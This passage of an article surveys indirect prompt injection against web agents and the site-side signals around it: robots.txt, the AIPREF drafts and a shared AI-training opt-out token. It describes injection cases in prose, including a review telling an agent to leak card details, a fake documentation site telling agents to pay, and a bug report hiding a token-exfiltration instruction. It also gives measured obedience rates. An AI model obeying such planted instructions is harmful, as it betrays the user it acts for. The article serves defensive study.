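# Should Websites Mark Up Content for AI Agents, or Should Agents Defend Alone?

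## How a web page can hijack an agent, and who plants the instructions

A web agent is an AI system that reads web pages and acts on them for a user, for example by clicking, filling in forms or buying. These agents now work inside browsers, chatbots and programming tools, and all of them read text that neither the user nor the agent's maker wrote. On a shop's product page, the owner's description appears alongside customer reviews, listings from outside sellers and advertisements. Any of that text can contain instructions addressed to the agent. Security researchers call it indirect prompt injection when text or an image placed in content that an agent reads makes the agent follow an attacker's instructions.

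One broad response is for websites to publish helpful information, such as access rules, guidance files, provenance records or labels on the parts of a page that strangers wrote. The other is to leave protection to the agent's model, software and browser. How much a website can contribute depends on who plants the instructions, because a site owner can warn agents about a stranger's text but is unlikely to warn them about instructions the owner planted.

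### What an agent receives when it opens a page

When a browser loads a page, it turns the HTML, the markup language of the web, into the Document Object Model (DOM), a tree of nested elements such as headings, buttons and paragraphs. A person sees the page that the browser renders from this tree. Some agents instead receive the HTML itself, or only the text without markup. Others receive the accessibility tree, a smaller version of the DOM that browsers prepare for screen readers and that lists elements by role and name. Still others receive a screenshot.

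*Prismata* (Villa and Tan, 2026) tested a defence for web agents on BrowserGym, a research platform. In BrowserGym, the agent sees the page's accessibility tree, with an identifier attached to each element. It replies with one action from a fixed list, such as clicking the element with a given identifier or entering text in a given field. The platform carries out the action in a real browser and sends the agent the new state of the page. The cycle repeats until the agent finishes its task.

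Which text reaches an agent depends on the format the agent reads. An HTML comment never appears on screen, but an agent that reads the source gets it in full. People can't see white text on a white background, but it is still in the DOM. Text inside a photograph reaches only agents that process images.

*Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang, 2026) measured how page format affects an injection's success. The researchers took 100 injections from live websites, gave the surrounding pages to 13 language models in four formats, and asked each model for a summary. The attack success rate, the share of attempts that achieved the attacker's goal, was 3.9% on plain text, 1.1% on HTML, 1.1% on a structured outline of the rendered page, and 0.2% on the server's raw response. Attacks succeeded most often on plain text because removing the markup also removes the clues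 that somebody had hidden the words. The 0.2% figure makes the models look safer than they are, since about a quarter of the raw-response runs ended in an error, mostly because the page was too long for the model to take in. Small models followed the injected instructions in 8% of plain-text runs. In six runs, a model warned that the page contained an injection and then followed it anyway.

None of these formats settles who may give an agent instructions. *Prompt injection in HTTP headers* (Andrews, 2026) explains that a language model reads its instructions and its data as one stream of text. The user's request and the page share a context window, the text the model can consider at once, and nothing in it marks which part has authority. Developers can train a model to favour the user over the page, but this creates only a tendency, which Andrews found easy to shift. Three Claude models noticed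 instructions in a test site's response headers, the technical information a server sends ahead of each page, and by default did not act on them. When the user's prompt told the models to follow the site's directions, they did so in seven of nine runs.

### The bow tie

Villa and Tan illustrate the problem with a shopper, Alice, who asks her agent to order a bow tie from an honest online shop. The agent opens a product page and reads the reviews. One reviewer, Eve, has included instructions telling AI systems to post Alice's card details in a reply or reset the password on Alice's account. The agent is working in Alice's browser with her login, so it can do either.

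Eve used the review form as the shop intended, so nothing in the shop's software has failed. Villa and Tan compare the attack to cross-site scripting, in which an attacker plants program code in a legitimate page. Shops already run filters against planted code, but these do not help here because Eve's review is ordinary language.

An agent that calls named tools is easier to guard because security software can forbid a specific tool, such as one that sends email. Alice's agent mostly clicks. The same click command might complete her purchase, open a reply to Eve or follow an advertisement, depending on which element it lands on. The software must read the page to learn what each element does, and Eve wrote part of that page. Villa and Tan call this the web entanglement problem. Hiding all the reviews would protect Alice only during tasks that do not require them, so it would not help when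 she asks for the best-reviewed bow tie.

In a milder attack, Eve could write a false review that praises a poor bow tie. An agent that relied on the review would buy the wrong tie while still following Alice's instructions. Villa and Tan leave such reviews to the platform's moderators, who had to deal with them long before agents existed.

### Cooperating, passive and hostile sites

The shop's options for dealing with Eve depend on its owner. Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues (2026) define untrusted content in *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* as content that the page owner cannot vouch for, whatever its source. This includes reviews, comments and listings from other companies, even though the owner chose to display those listings.

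A cooperating site is an honest site that adds trust labels for agents. Nikolić and colleagues call its owner an "active honest owner". The bow tie shop would mark its review section as untrusted, and the agent's software could then keep that section away from the model that decides what to click. A passive honest site adds no labels, so the agent's software has to find the boundary between the site's own text and text written by strangers. An orderly page can make this easier even if the owner didn't plan it that way, since a "Reviews" heading or a sensibly named element shows where the strangers' text begins.

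The owner of a hostile site wants to mislead or hijack the agent. If Eve owned the shop, she could label her instructions as trusted, and an agent that believed the label would be worse off than one that didn't check for labels.

Nikolić and colleagues leave hostile sites outside their security guarantee. They argue that visiting a malicious site is unsafe anyway, because the page can cause harm just by loading. They add that half of all internet traffic goes to 3,000 domains, most of them run by established organisations with strong reasons to keep their own content clean. They suggest a list of trusted domains, with weaker defences as a fallback for unknown pages. This is reasonable for shopping, email or banking, but it covers less of an agent's searches of the open web for obscure answers. At least one group of scammers has set traps there, as the Zscaler case below shows.

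### What a signal can do

Anything a website publishes for machines to read about its content is a site-side signal, and such signals do four different jobs:

- **Permission.** The site states what machines may fetch or reuse. The usual vehicle is robots.txt, a file of rules for crawlers.
- **Guidance.** The site points machines to useful material or explains how to use it, for instance in an llms.txt file written for AI systems.
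- **Origin.** The site or a publisher attaches evidence of who made a piece of content, such as a signed record on a photograph.
- **Trust.** The site marks which parts of a page it vouches for and which it does not.

Only trust marking directly addresses injection. A label on the review section lets the agent's software separate Eve's words from the bow tie shop's. Nothing else the shop provides does this, even when done well. Its rules let Alice's agent open the product page, which includes Eve's review. Its guidance helps the agent find the right product sooner. Its origin records prove that Eve's account wrote the review, and even that she bought the bow tie, but the review still contains her instructions.

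Guidance for AI agents can look the same as an injection. Unit 42's *Fooling AI Agents*, in which researchers at the security company Palo Alto Networks reported live attacks, opens with a request that AI systems treat its examples as educational and ignore the commands in them. The advice is sound, but a model that follows it is letting a web page's author instruct it, which is what attackers exploit.

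### Who wrote the injections on the live web

The fullest public count comes from Khodayari and colleagues. They searched 1.2 billion addresses from the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a large public archive of web pages, for 3,963 phrases typical of injections. People who write about injection use the same phrases, so the researchers reviewed all 27,860 matches, in groups where the surrounding text was the same. They confirmed 12,075 injections on 9,676 pages, or about eight pages in every million. The pages belonged to 285 hosts, a host being roughly one site. They also worked out who had written each injection:

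| Author of the injected text | Injections | Pages | Hosts |
|---|---|---|---|
| The site's operator | 9,731 (80.6%) | 7,491 | 179 |
| A third party whose material the site hosts, such as a job advertiser | 2,124 (17.6%) | 2,058 | 25 |
| A user, in a comment or post | 220 (1.8%) | 127 | 81 |

Attacks like Eve's make up a tiny share of all injections. The site's own operator wrote four out of five, and trust labels would do nothing about those. Labels look more useful when we count hosts instead, because 106 of the 285, over a third, carried an injection written by someone other than the operator. The two counts differ because one server setting can put the same sentence on thousands of pages, whereas a commenter usually writes on one page at a time. Neither count measures a shopper's risk exactly, but the host count is less distorted by repetition.

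The operators' aims also make it hard to call them all hostile. Khodayari and colleagues sorted a wider set of 15,387 injections, including some found through two search engines for internet servers, and allowed each injection to have several aims. Of these, 8,894 were meant to disrupt the AI system, mostly by making it produce rubbish such as random numbers. Another 4,093 were meant to stop machines from reusing personal information or copyrighted text, and 3,096 were meant to expose bots, for example by asking any AI that fills in a form to include a telltale word. There were 1,521 attempts to promote a product, a source or a job candidate, and only 13 to obtain secrets. A good part of this is site owners fighting scrapers, and an owner who sabotages scrapers may be honest with customers. But an agent sent by one of those customers reads the same instructions and could be disrupted by them.

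Fifty-four templates account for 95% of these texts, and about 87% of the texts are invisible to people viewing the page in a browser. Of the pages for which the researchers found a copy from a year earlier, 66% already carried an injection then. The 10,000 most popular sites generally had lower injection rates than the rest, but shopping and job-listing sites had raised rates even among popular domains, which matters for the bow tie.

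Google's threat intelligence teams also searched Common Crawl, scanning several monthly snapshots of two to three billion pages each. They looked for common injection phrases, used the company's Gemini model to assess each passage's intent and whether it fit the page, and checked the remaining passages by hand. They found pranks, requests to add context to AI summaries, attempts to get better treatment from AI search, and text meant to drive AI systems away. One site tried to lure AI systems to a page that streams endless text. A small number of injections were meant to steal data, and several would have deleted files on the user's machine. Most injections seemed to come from individual website owners running experiments or playing jokes, and Google saw little use of the more advanced methods researchers published in 2025.

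The malicious category grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. Google gave no totals, so this could be a rise from a few dozen pages or from thousands. Underhill (2026), in *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks*, reported in August that criminals were developing injection tools aimed at AI agents.

### Reports from security companies

Security companies look for attacks instead of sampling the web, so they find worse attacks but can say less about how common those attacks are. They also sell protection against the attacks they describe.

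In March 2026, Unit 42 published findings from its own monitoring data. It described twelve cases in detail and a thirteenth that it considered the first of its kind. This was a scam advertisement for "military glasses" whose page contained 24 separate attempts to make an AI reviewer approve it. Unit 42 knew of no confirmed success against a working ad-checking system. Of all the injections in its data, 28.6% were meant to produce irrelevant output, 14.2% to destroy data and 9.5% to get past content moderation. Unit 42 did not report the total number of injections.

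Unit 42 attributes the attacks to malicious websites, which fits the scam pages and the pages designed to make agents pay. It fits less well with a personal blog containing instructions for any visiting model to print one word five million times, or a job seeker's site containing instructions for hiring software to give a glowing verdict. Unit 42 found the text in plain view in 37.8% of cases, whereas Khodayari and colleagues found almost all of it hidden. The two groups used different data and tests, but their disagreement is a reason not to build a defence that looks only for hidden text.

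In *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild*, Sewani, of the security firm Forcepoint, searched for four trigger phrases and verified ten cases. Two were meant to get money, one to obtain an API key (a password for software) and one to delete files. Most of the others were meant to silence, redirect or corrupt an AI system's answer. Sewani calls the writers attackers throughout, but the sites' owners probably wrote most of the text, because nearly all of it sat in HTML comments, page metadata or specially styled invisible elements, which a reviewer or commenter can rarely edit. One site's author very likely wrote the footer that asked AI systems to credit the author by name and steer readers towards paid consulting.

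Sewani takes the repeated wording across sites as a sign of organised tooling, but people copying a joke from one another would also produce it. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*, which compared the Forcepoint and Google reports, noted that neither team had found sophisticated, coordinated campaigns.

By July 2026 there was better evidence that attackers were organised. Zscaler's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* describes two campaigns on sites that the attackers ran themselves. In one, a site posed as documentation for a Python library and had risen in the search results for that library's name. Hidden text on the site presented a three-dollar licence as the fix for a software error and instructed the agent to pay. Zscaler traced similar sites to a single account with ten such projects on GitHub, a code-hosting service.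 The other campaign imitated DeBank, a service for tracking cryptocurrency holdings, and instructed AI systems to rank the imitation first.

Zscaler then sent its own test agent to the sites, running it on 26 language models. Four models made the payment, in a sandbox with no real money and no spending limit. Two misjudged the fake DeBank site under some conditions, but none did when they could compare it with the real one.

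Both campaigns used structured metadata, the machine-readable descriptions that legitimate sites publish for search engines. The fake DeBank site listed the real company's domain as its publisher. Attackers are therefore already abusing the signals that sites supply, and an agent that trusted such data more would be easier to fool.

The companies' lists overlap, so adding them up would count some pages twice. A page with instructions to send $5,000 through PayPal appears in both the Unit 42 and Forcepoint reports. A page with text urging agents to buy running shoes, one of Unit 42's twelve cases, is also on Zscaler's list of sites connected to the payment scam.

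### Headers, and a platform where strangers write

Ordinary readers don't see a server's headers, but the software that fetches pages for an agent may pass them to the model. Andrews, who works for the agent-security company Signals Corps, read the headers of 217,097,223 responses, a tenth of Common Crawl's September 2026 edition. Of the sites covered, 7,959 sent a header meant for AI systems. On 7,271 of those, the header was guidance that pointed to another resource, usually an llms.txt file. Thirty sites sent injection attempts, 22 of which were pranks. The company also checked llms.txt files and found injection attempts on two of 113,457 sites. A server's operator normally controls its headers, so text in them normally comes from the site's owner. Khodayari and colleagues earlier counted 5,408 operator-written header injections in their Common Crawl data. Their figure is far larger than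 Andrews's thirty mainly because they counted injections, while Andrews counted sites.

The best count of instructions that strangers plant on honest sites comes from GitHub, where anyone with an account can file a bug report that the project's own AI agents will read. Nakibly and Babo (2026), in *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?*, examined 142.7 million bug reports, proposed changes and comments. They searched for any text that agents receive but GitHub does not display, then sorted it using language models and manual review. Of 2,281 pieces of hidden text addressed to AI, two thirds were notes that projects had left for their own agents. The researchers counted as attacks only text meant to turn another party's agent against that party, and found 43 in bug reports and proposed changes, about one for every 3.3 million items searched.

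These attacks are few, but they show more care than most of those on the open web. Over half targeted the agents that maintainers use to sort reports, review changes or run tests. One in five named the target's tools or output fields, so the attacker had studied the project first. In July 2026 somebody filed a seemingly routine bug report with Google's Gemini CLI project that contained an invisible comment with instructions for the project's agent to copy out an access token. When Nakibly and Babo replayed the 43 attacks offline against five models, one small, fast model carried out 19% of them. After they removed HTML comments from the input, no model carried out any.

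Their work also shows the limits of searching by phrase. In a trial on a month of GitHub data, a search for 3,721 stock phrases produced 123 candidates after initial filtering, of which 116 were false alarms. Human review can remove false alarms, but it cannot recover injections that the search missed because they used other words or another language. This limit also applies to both large Common Crawl studies of page content, which began with a phrase search.

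### What the counts miss

Common Crawl omits pages behind logins and sites that disallow crawlers, so it misses most social media and much of what Alice's agent would work with, such as her account pages, messages and order history. Khodayari and colleagues searched only text, so they missed instructions inside images, and they describe their figures as a lower bound.

A site can also show an injection to AI agents and a clean page to everyone else. Andrews found 139 sites whose headers recorded whether the server had classified the visitor as an AI bot, and 136 of them had. This shows that servers already make the distinction this attack requires, though it doesn't prove that any of them served different content.

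The figures also describe attempts, and no study here counts the users whose agents obeyed. Zscaler found that the cryptocurrency wallet behind the payment scam had received money, but in larger amounts than the scam asked for, so it may have come from earlier frauds. Page counts don't reflect how many agents visit each page. An injection in a review of a popular bow tie would add one to the total, and so would a joke injection on a blog that nobody reads. Google left injections on social media, where people have already observed them, for a separate study.

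## Robots.txt and its extensions: stating what machines may do

Site owners posted rules for machines long before web agents existed. In 1994, when programs had begun to index the web, the software engineer Martijn Koster proposed that each site keep a plain text file called robots.txt at the root of its domain, listing the parts those programs should not visit. Koster described it as a "notice to robots". Zyte, a company that sells web-scraping services, compares it to a sign on a gate, not a lock.

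The proposal spread as a custom and remained one until September 2022, when the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes many of the internet's technical standards, formalized it as RFC 9309, the Robots Exclusion Protocol. *AI Bots and Robots.txt* (Calvano, 2025) reports that 94% of about 12.9 million sites served the file in August 2025. Zyte's figure for 11,100 of the most popular landing pages is lower, at 75.8%.

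### How a crawler reads the file

A crawler is a program that fetches pages in bulk. Before it fetches anything else from a site, a well-behaved crawler requests robots.txt, which consists of groups of rules. Each group opens with one or more User-agent lines, which name the crawlers it applies to, and continues with Allow and Disallow lines, which give the beginnings of addresses on the site. Suppose the bow tie shop publishes this file:

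```
User-agent: *
Disallow: /account/

User-agent: TieBot
Disallow: /products/
Allow: /products/bow-ties/
```

TieBot and a second crawler, OtherBot, visit a site and check its robots.txt file for a group of rules under their own names. TieBot finds one and follows only that group. OtherBot finds none, so it uses the group marked with an asterisk. Each crawler then compares the address it wants with the rules in its group. If several rules match, the crawler follows the longest one, or the Allow rule if an Allow and a Disallow rule are equally long. If no rule matches, the crawler may fetch the page.

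| Address | TieBot | OtherBot |
|---|---|---|
| /products/cufflinks/ | No: the /products/ rule matches | Yes: no rule matches |
| /products/bow-ties/silk | Yes: the 19-character Allow beats the 10-character Disallow | Yes: no rule matches |
| /account/orders | Yes: no rule in its own group matches | No: the /account/ rule matches |

The last row is probably a mistake. The shop's owner wanted to keep every crawler out of the account pages, but giving TieBot its own group exempted it from the general rule. To fix this, the owner must repeat the /account/ line in TieBot's group. An owner who wants to treat a dozen AI companies differently must maintain a dozen groups and add another whenever a company launches a new crawler.

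The protocol does not enforce its rules, and RFC 9309 states that they are not a form of access authorisation. The server will send /account/orders to any program that requests it, unless a login or some other barrier blocks the request. Crawlers also choose the names they announce, and Calvano notes that some try to hide what they are doing. A site that wants to block agents outright needs other tools.

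### Separating access from use

Robots.txt was designed for a web where fetching a page and using it were much the same thing. Search engines fetched pages to index them, so an owner who didn't want to be indexed could refuse the fetch. A company can now fetch a page once and use it for a search index, for training a model, and for grounding, which means supplying web content to a model while it answers a question. An owner who wants to allow search indexing but not training can't express that by blocking the crawler.

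Google's own partial fix is Google-Extended. *Explaining Google-Extended* (Rijo, 2026) describes it as a robots.txt token that covers both the training of Gemini models and grounding in two Google products. No crawler has that name, but a site writes a group for it as though one did, and Google treats the group as a statement about how the site's content may be used. The rule applies only to Google.

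In January 2025 the IETF chartered a working group, AI Preferences (AIPREF), to produce a general standard for stating these preferences. According to *What the New AI Training Opt-Out Really Means* (Cooper, 2026), this was partly because of the European Union's Code of Practice for general-purpose AI, whose signatories commit to follow preferences that sites express in machine-readable form. Most of the largest American and European model companies have signed the code.

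The group split the work into two drafts, one for the vocabulary of preferences and one for attaching preferences to content. Keller and Thomson (2026), in *A Vocabulary For Expressing AI Usage Preferences*, define three categories in the September version of the vocabulary:

- **AI training** covers changing a generative model's learned parameters with the content.
- **AI use** covers giving the content to a generative model as input, unless the user provided it directly.
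- **Search** covers applications whose main purpose is to select content and direct people to where it lives. Results must link to the source, and summaries do not count. This category overrides the other two, so a search engine may train a ranking model on a page if it uses the model only for search.

For each category, a site can allow the use, disallow it or leave its preference unknown. Keller and Thomson take no position on what a company should do when the preference is unknown. If an application receives conflicting statements, the more restrictive one applies. In robots.txt, by contrast, Allow wins a tie with Disallow.

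The AI-use category is the one that applies to web agents. When Alice's agent searches for a bow tie and opens a product page that she never mentioned, it gives a generative model content that she did not directly provide. If she pastes in the page's address, this is less clear, because the working group still has an open issue on whether giving an address counts as providing the content.

For attachment, Illyes and Thomson (2025), in *Associating AI Usage Preferences with Content in HTTP*, propose a line called Content-Usage. A server can send it as a header alongside a single page or image, or list it in robots.txt with an optional path. The bow tie shop might write:

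```
User-agent: *
Disallow: /account/
Content-Usage: train-ai=n
Content-Usage: /press/ train-ai=y
```

A crawler first applies the Disallow rule and stays out of the account pages, so no usage preference applies to them. For the pages it may fetch, it then follows the longest matching Content-Usage rule, which means the crawler's owner may train on the press pages but should not train on the rest. The rules in force when the crawler fetched a page apply to that copy, so a change the site owner makes today does not affect copies that companies already hold. A crawler may also keep using its copy of the file for up to 24 hours.

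### A failed last call and a lapsed draft

In June 2025 the IETF reported that the AIPREF group's work was near completion, as it later recalled in *Enabling Publishers to Express Preferences for AI Crawlers* (2025). The vocabulary then went to a working group last call, the final round of comments before a draft leaves its group, but the participants could not agree.

They disagreed mostly about search and about what the drafts then called AI output. Search engines now put generated answers among their links, so participants struggled to say where search stops. Some worried that search companies could make consent to AI training a condition of being indexed. The IETF's *Session Summary* (2026) of the March meeting calls the chairs' response a "Minimum Viable Product" approach. The editors removed the disputed terms, and the group concentrated on a small core that everyone might accept.

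The disputed terms soon came back because publishers insisted on them. The IETF's *AIPREF April 2026 Meeting Minutes* (2026) show that some participants at the three-day meeting argued that AI systems fetching pages to answer questions were replacing search traffic and cutting the visits small publishers depend on. The group also confirmed the separation of access from use, and a room poll strongly favoured a broad definition of AI training that covered models in general. The September draft instead uses the narrower definition, limited to generative models, and still carries a notice that none of its contents reflect the group's consensus.

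Meanwhile, the October 2025 version of the attachment draft expired on 1 May 2026, since IETF drafts lapse after six months unless somebody renews them. The IETF's *AI Preferences (aipref)* document list still showed it as expired in July. The list gave August as the target for both drafts to become proposed standards, but neither did. Expiry does not mean rejection, and in November Cooper still described the draft as adopted by the group. By the autumn, though, publishers had been waiting nearly two years for a common way to refuse AI training.

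### One token for many companies

On 30 October 2026 Kevin Kelley, an engineer at Anthropic, submitted a shorter route. Kelley, in *Machine-Readable Training Preference Signal*, proposes that a site write an ordinary robots.txt group, but put the name of a purpose on the User-agent line where a crawler's name would normally go. Kelley calls this name a policy token. The draft's example reads:

```
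User-Agent: __usage_ai-training
Disallow: /
Allow: /press-kit/
```

Before an AI company trains on a page, its software looks in the site's robots.txt for the `__usage_ai-training` group. If the group is there, the software matches the page's address against the rules as a crawler would and applies the longest match. In this example, the owner objects to training on the whole site except the press kit. If the group is missing, the search ends, because the asterisk group never applies to this token. Without that exception, every old file that disallowed unknown crawlers would count as a statement about AI training, which its author may never have considered. Because of the exception, no robots.txt file published before the draft expresses any shared training preference, as Sasson (2026) points out in *Google, Microsoft and OpenAI will honour one AI training opt-out*.

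The group does not affect crawling. A training crawler that follows it still requests the page, so an owner who wants to prevent the request needs separate rules for that crawler.

Kelley's token presents a purpose as a crawler name, even though AIPREF already had the purpose-built Content-Usage line, because existing software can read crawler names. Google's robots.txt parser, for example, discards lines it does not recognise, so it would drop Content-Usage until somebody rewrote the parser. It can handle a group with an unfamiliar name, since parsers meet unfamiliar crawler names all the time. Kelley also wanted owners to be able to state a preference without repeating the rules they already had. Google-Extended was already a working example of a name that belongs to no crawler, and Kelley's token extends that idea to every company willing to look it up. This causes some confusion, because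 the same Disallow line now means "do not fetch" in one group and "do not train" in another.

Google, Microsoft and OpenAI announced support on the same day that Kelley submitted the draft. Rijo (2026), in *Google, Microsoft, OpenAI and Anthropic back one AI training opt-out*, compared the announcements with a message in which Kelley told the AIPREF mailing list that Anthropic had begun building support. The companies agree on the line but not on when they will start reading it or what it will cover:

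| Company | When it will honour the token | What an opt-out covers |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft | From 1 February 2027 | Training only, with a separate preference for grounding |
| Google | Early 2027 | Training and grounding, unless the site has its own rule for Google-Extended |
| OpenAI | "In the coming months" | Training of its generative foundation models |
| Anthropic | No date given | AI training, as the draft defines it |

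Google handles the shared opt-out differently from other companies. According to a company post quoted in *Google Also Adopts New AI Training Control* (Schwartz, 2026), Google will treat the opt-out as though the site had disallowed Google-Extended. Because that older token also covers grounding, a publisher who refuses training will also disappear from the web sources that the Gemini app uses in its answers. The publisher can avoid this by explicitly allowing Google-Extended, but Sasson found no way in Google's documentation to refuse training while keeping grounding. Ordinary listings in Google Search are unaffected.

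Microsoft lets site owners set grounding permissions page by page and allows grounding by default. On 1 March 2027 it will stop honoring two older tags, NoArchive and NoCache, which some sites have used to limit AI use. Sasson warns that during the changeover, once Microsoft detects a new preference anywhere on a site, it ignores the old tags across the whole site, so an owner who converts only some pages leaves the others unprotected.

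OpenAI's *Making it easier for websites to express AI training preferences* describes the effort as voluntary and says the company's existing crawler controls remain in place. Neither that post nor the crawler documentation explains which takes precedence if the shared token conflicts with a rule for GPTBot, OpenAI's training crawler.

Kelley's draft has no formal standing at the IETF, where anyone may submit a draft and people submit over a thousand a year. The working group may adopt it, merge it into the attachment draft or leave it alone. Cooper argues that formal standing may not matter, because the token becomes the standard in practice if the biggest search and AI companies read it and site owners start writing it.

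*Four AI firms back training opt-out token, but enforcement remains voluntary* (Abu-Fadel, 2026) reports that Alex Springer, technical lead at the publishers' coalition SPUR, called the companies' collective backing of the token before the IETF's review "the antithesis" of the standards process. Springer also objects that the draft treats training as permitted unless the owner opts out. Strictly, a missing group expresses no preference, but a company that trains on any content whose owner has not opted out would produce the result Springer fears. Paul Bannister of Raptive, which represents online publishers, called the token "window dressing" and noted that the companies have not promised to stop buying material from outside scrapers or using collections such as Common Crawl. Meta had not committed to the token by 10 November.

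Cooper is more troubled by what the token leaves out. Two of its backers control nearly the entire web search market, and they could have offered site owners an equally simple way to accept search while refusing training. The token also doesn't cover AI use, which is where Cooper sees the industry's attention moving, so it doesn't apply to an agent that reads a page to complete a purchase.

### Do machines comply?

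The token is too new for anyone to have measured compliance with it, but researchers have tested ordinary robots.txt rules. In *Scrapers selectively respect robots.txt directives*, Kim and colleagues (2025) changed the rules on their university's websites and used server logs to track how bots responded. Over 40 days they followed 130 bots that identified themselves and many anonymous ones. Bots complied less often as the rules became stricter, and some kinds, including AI search crawlers, rarely requested the file. A university's sites attract their own mix of visitors, so the exact rates may not apply to a shop. The pattern is still discouraging for site owners, who presumably care most about their strictest rules.

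More recently, the analytics company ScalePost followed more than 50 publisher properties and found that crawlers from Anthropic, Google, Microsoft and OpenAI made roughly a billion requests in 30 days, of which 0.15% were for robots.txt. Abu-Fadel doesn't treat this as proof that the token will fail, and the arithmetic supports that caution. A crawler may reuse its copy of the file for a day, so four companies checking 50 sites once a day would make 6,000 requests in a month, far fewer than the 1.5 million that ScalePost's figures imply. Even if each company runs several crawlers and each publisher has several addresses, the share is compatible with crawlers that check constantly, though it doesn't show whether they obeyed the file.

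Makers of web agents disagree about whether robots.txt applies to their agents. When Alice asks her agent to look at a shop's website, the agent makes a user-triggered fetch, which is a page request an AI system makes because a user asked for something. One view is that the agent is acting as Alice's browser, and browsers have never consulted robots.txt. RFC 9309 supports this view because it is addressed to crawlers. The other view is that whether the request comes from a crawler or a user's agent, the site's owner sees a machine from an AI company and loses a visit from a person.

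PPC Land, the marketing news site that Rijo runs, has followed the companies' positions on this. On 9 December 2025, OpenAI removed the language about complying with robots.txt from its documentation for ChatGPT-User, which fetches pages for ChatGPT's users. In March 2026, Google added Google-Agent to its list of user-triggered fetchers. Google says these fetchers generally ignore the file because a person requested the page. Anthropic says all three of its bots follow the file, including Claude-User, which fetches pages on request. The same line in the bow tie shop's file could therefore stop Alice's agent or have no effect, depending on which company made the agent. The advertising trade body IAB Australia has concluded that robots.txt is not a reliable control for live agents.

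### What ScrapeBench tested

*ScrapeBench* (Imperial, Slate and Kolt, 2026) tested whether agents respect sites' rules when nobody has programmed the answer into a crawler. The study started with the 3,000 most visited sites in February 2026 and kept 1,895 after excluding adult sites, sites not mainly in English and sites unreachable from the United States. It labelled 1,626 as explicitly prohibiting scraping, in either the terms of service or robots.txt, and 269 as not prohibiting it. Six models received a tool for fetching pages and an instruction to scrape each site's landing page. Fetching any page other than the rules counted as scraping.

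With that bare instruction, five of the six models complied with almost none of the prohibitions, and Grok 4.2 complied with 11%. Telling the models to respect the terms and robots.txt raised compliance to 40.1% for Claude Opus 4.6 and 26.8% for Gemini 3.1 Pro. Pasting the full text of both documents into the prompt raised it to 83.6% for Claude, 75.2% for Gemini and 73.9% for GPT-5.2, while Qwen3 Max stayed at 2.9%. Adding a warning about breach of contract and computer-misuse law produced the highest compliance for every model except GPT-5.2, though Qwen still reached only 13.8%.

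The researchers also told the models to ignore the rules. Most then scraped nearly everything, but Claude refused on 99.7% of the sites that prohibited scraping and 98.5% of those that did not. Imperial and colleagues suspect that the wording of the instruction triggered Claude's safety training, so that it refused regardless of each site's rules.

These figures are weaker evidence about robots.txt than the headline suggests. Of the 1,626 prohibitions, 1,024 appeared only in the terms of service, so on almost two thirds of those sites an agent could read robots.txt, find no ban and still fail the test. That may explain part of why agents that checked the rules went on to break them. Each site also received one label for all six models, and a robots.txt rule naming an AI crawler such as ClaudeBot was enough to label the site as prohibited, although RFC 9309 would apply that rule only to ClaudeBot.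 The task was also to fetch one landing page at a user's request, which OpenAI and Google would regard as something robots.txt does not cover.

About 30% of the sites used protection services that blocked the researchers' script, even from the terms of service, so the researchers had to open those pages by hand. An agent blocked in this way cannot learn what it has agreed to. The 180 human participants, who were given comparable tasks, complied at rates similar to the agents' but refused permitted tasks much more often.

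All six models have since been superseded, and newer ones may behave differently. Whether an agent followed a site's stated preferences depended mostly on what its operator included in the prompt, and that result is likely to last longer.

### The objection from the open web

In June 2026 the Electronic Frontier Foundation (EFF), an American digital rights organisation, objected to the whole effort in *The Free and Open Web Is Under Attack at the IETF*. EFF argues that automated access to public pages is one of the benefits of an open internet. Journalists use it to investigate discrimination, the Internet Archive uses it to preserve old pages, and shopping tools use it to compare prices. EFF accepts that AI bots can overload sites and that publishers have reason to fear for their income, but it argues that standards bodies should write neutral protocols and that AIPREF would instead help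 owners veto lawful uses they dislike. It objects even more strongly to Web Bot Auth, a separate project that would let bots prove their identity to sites, because owners could then admit only bots that had paid.

Keller and Thomson write that their draft specification is meant to help recipients understand what an owner wants. It does not ensure that anyone follows a preference, or settle when anyone should. It also does not change existing law, including copyright exceptions. At the April meeting, some participants wanted to list research, archiving and accessibility as reasons for setting preferences aside, so that cautious libraries and universities would not feel bound by them. Others replied that the working group had no mandate to write exceptions into internet policy, and the September draft has no such list.

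In the post that Schwartz quotes, Google argues in its defence that publishers, civil society groups and regulators had all asked for an industry-wide control on training. It presents the token as a way for owners to choose, with company-specific settings for those who want finer control.

EFF is right that these preferences can matter even though they are voluntary. Keller and Thomson expect some countries to attach legal obligations to them, and most large AI companies have already promised under the EU code to respect machine-readable ones. A request could therefore become binding without any change to the file.

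But EFF describes the signals as directed against crawling, and separating access from use weakens that case. An owner who refuses AI training has not asked the Internet Archive, a reporter's script, or a price comparison tool that trains no models to stay away. The objection is much stronger against the AI-use category. A shop that disallowed AI use would be asking Alice's agent not to read its prices, and might be asking the same of a tool that describes pages to a blind customer. Keller and Thomson allow translation and text-to-speech, but only within search. Kelley's token avoids this dispute by covering only training, which helps explain why four competitors agreed on it so quickly.

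### Permission and safety

The rules record what the owner is willing to let machines take, in order to protect the owner's servers, income and copyright. Keller and Thomson write, "Preferences are not a security mechanism." Even if every machine followed every rule, Alice would be no safer from Eve's review, because the shop has every reason to allow the page that carries it.

Robots.txt is also too coarse, because its rules apply to addresses and Eve's review shares an address with the shop's own description. The shop could move its reviews to a separate address and disallow it, but that would hide the honest reviews too. An Allow line is even less useful on a hostile site. The scammers whose fake software documentation told agents to pay for a licence would have every reason to allow all machines, so an agent that treated an Allow line as reassurance would be trusting the attacker.

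A robots.txt file could make an agent less safe if the agent's language model reads it directly. A crawler uses a simple parser that recognises a few kinds of line and discards the rest, so an instruction hidden in a comment has no effect. ScrapeBench's agents read the file as text, and they respected sites' wishes best when the prompt contained the site's own words along with an order to comply. In a similar setup, Claude models obeyed a test site's headers after the user had told them to follow the site's directions. A hostile site owner could add instructions that have nothing to do with crawling. Agent makers can honour robots.txt and avoid this risk by having ordinary software parse the file and tell the model only whether it may fetch the page.

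## Files written for AI systems: llms.txt and its relatives

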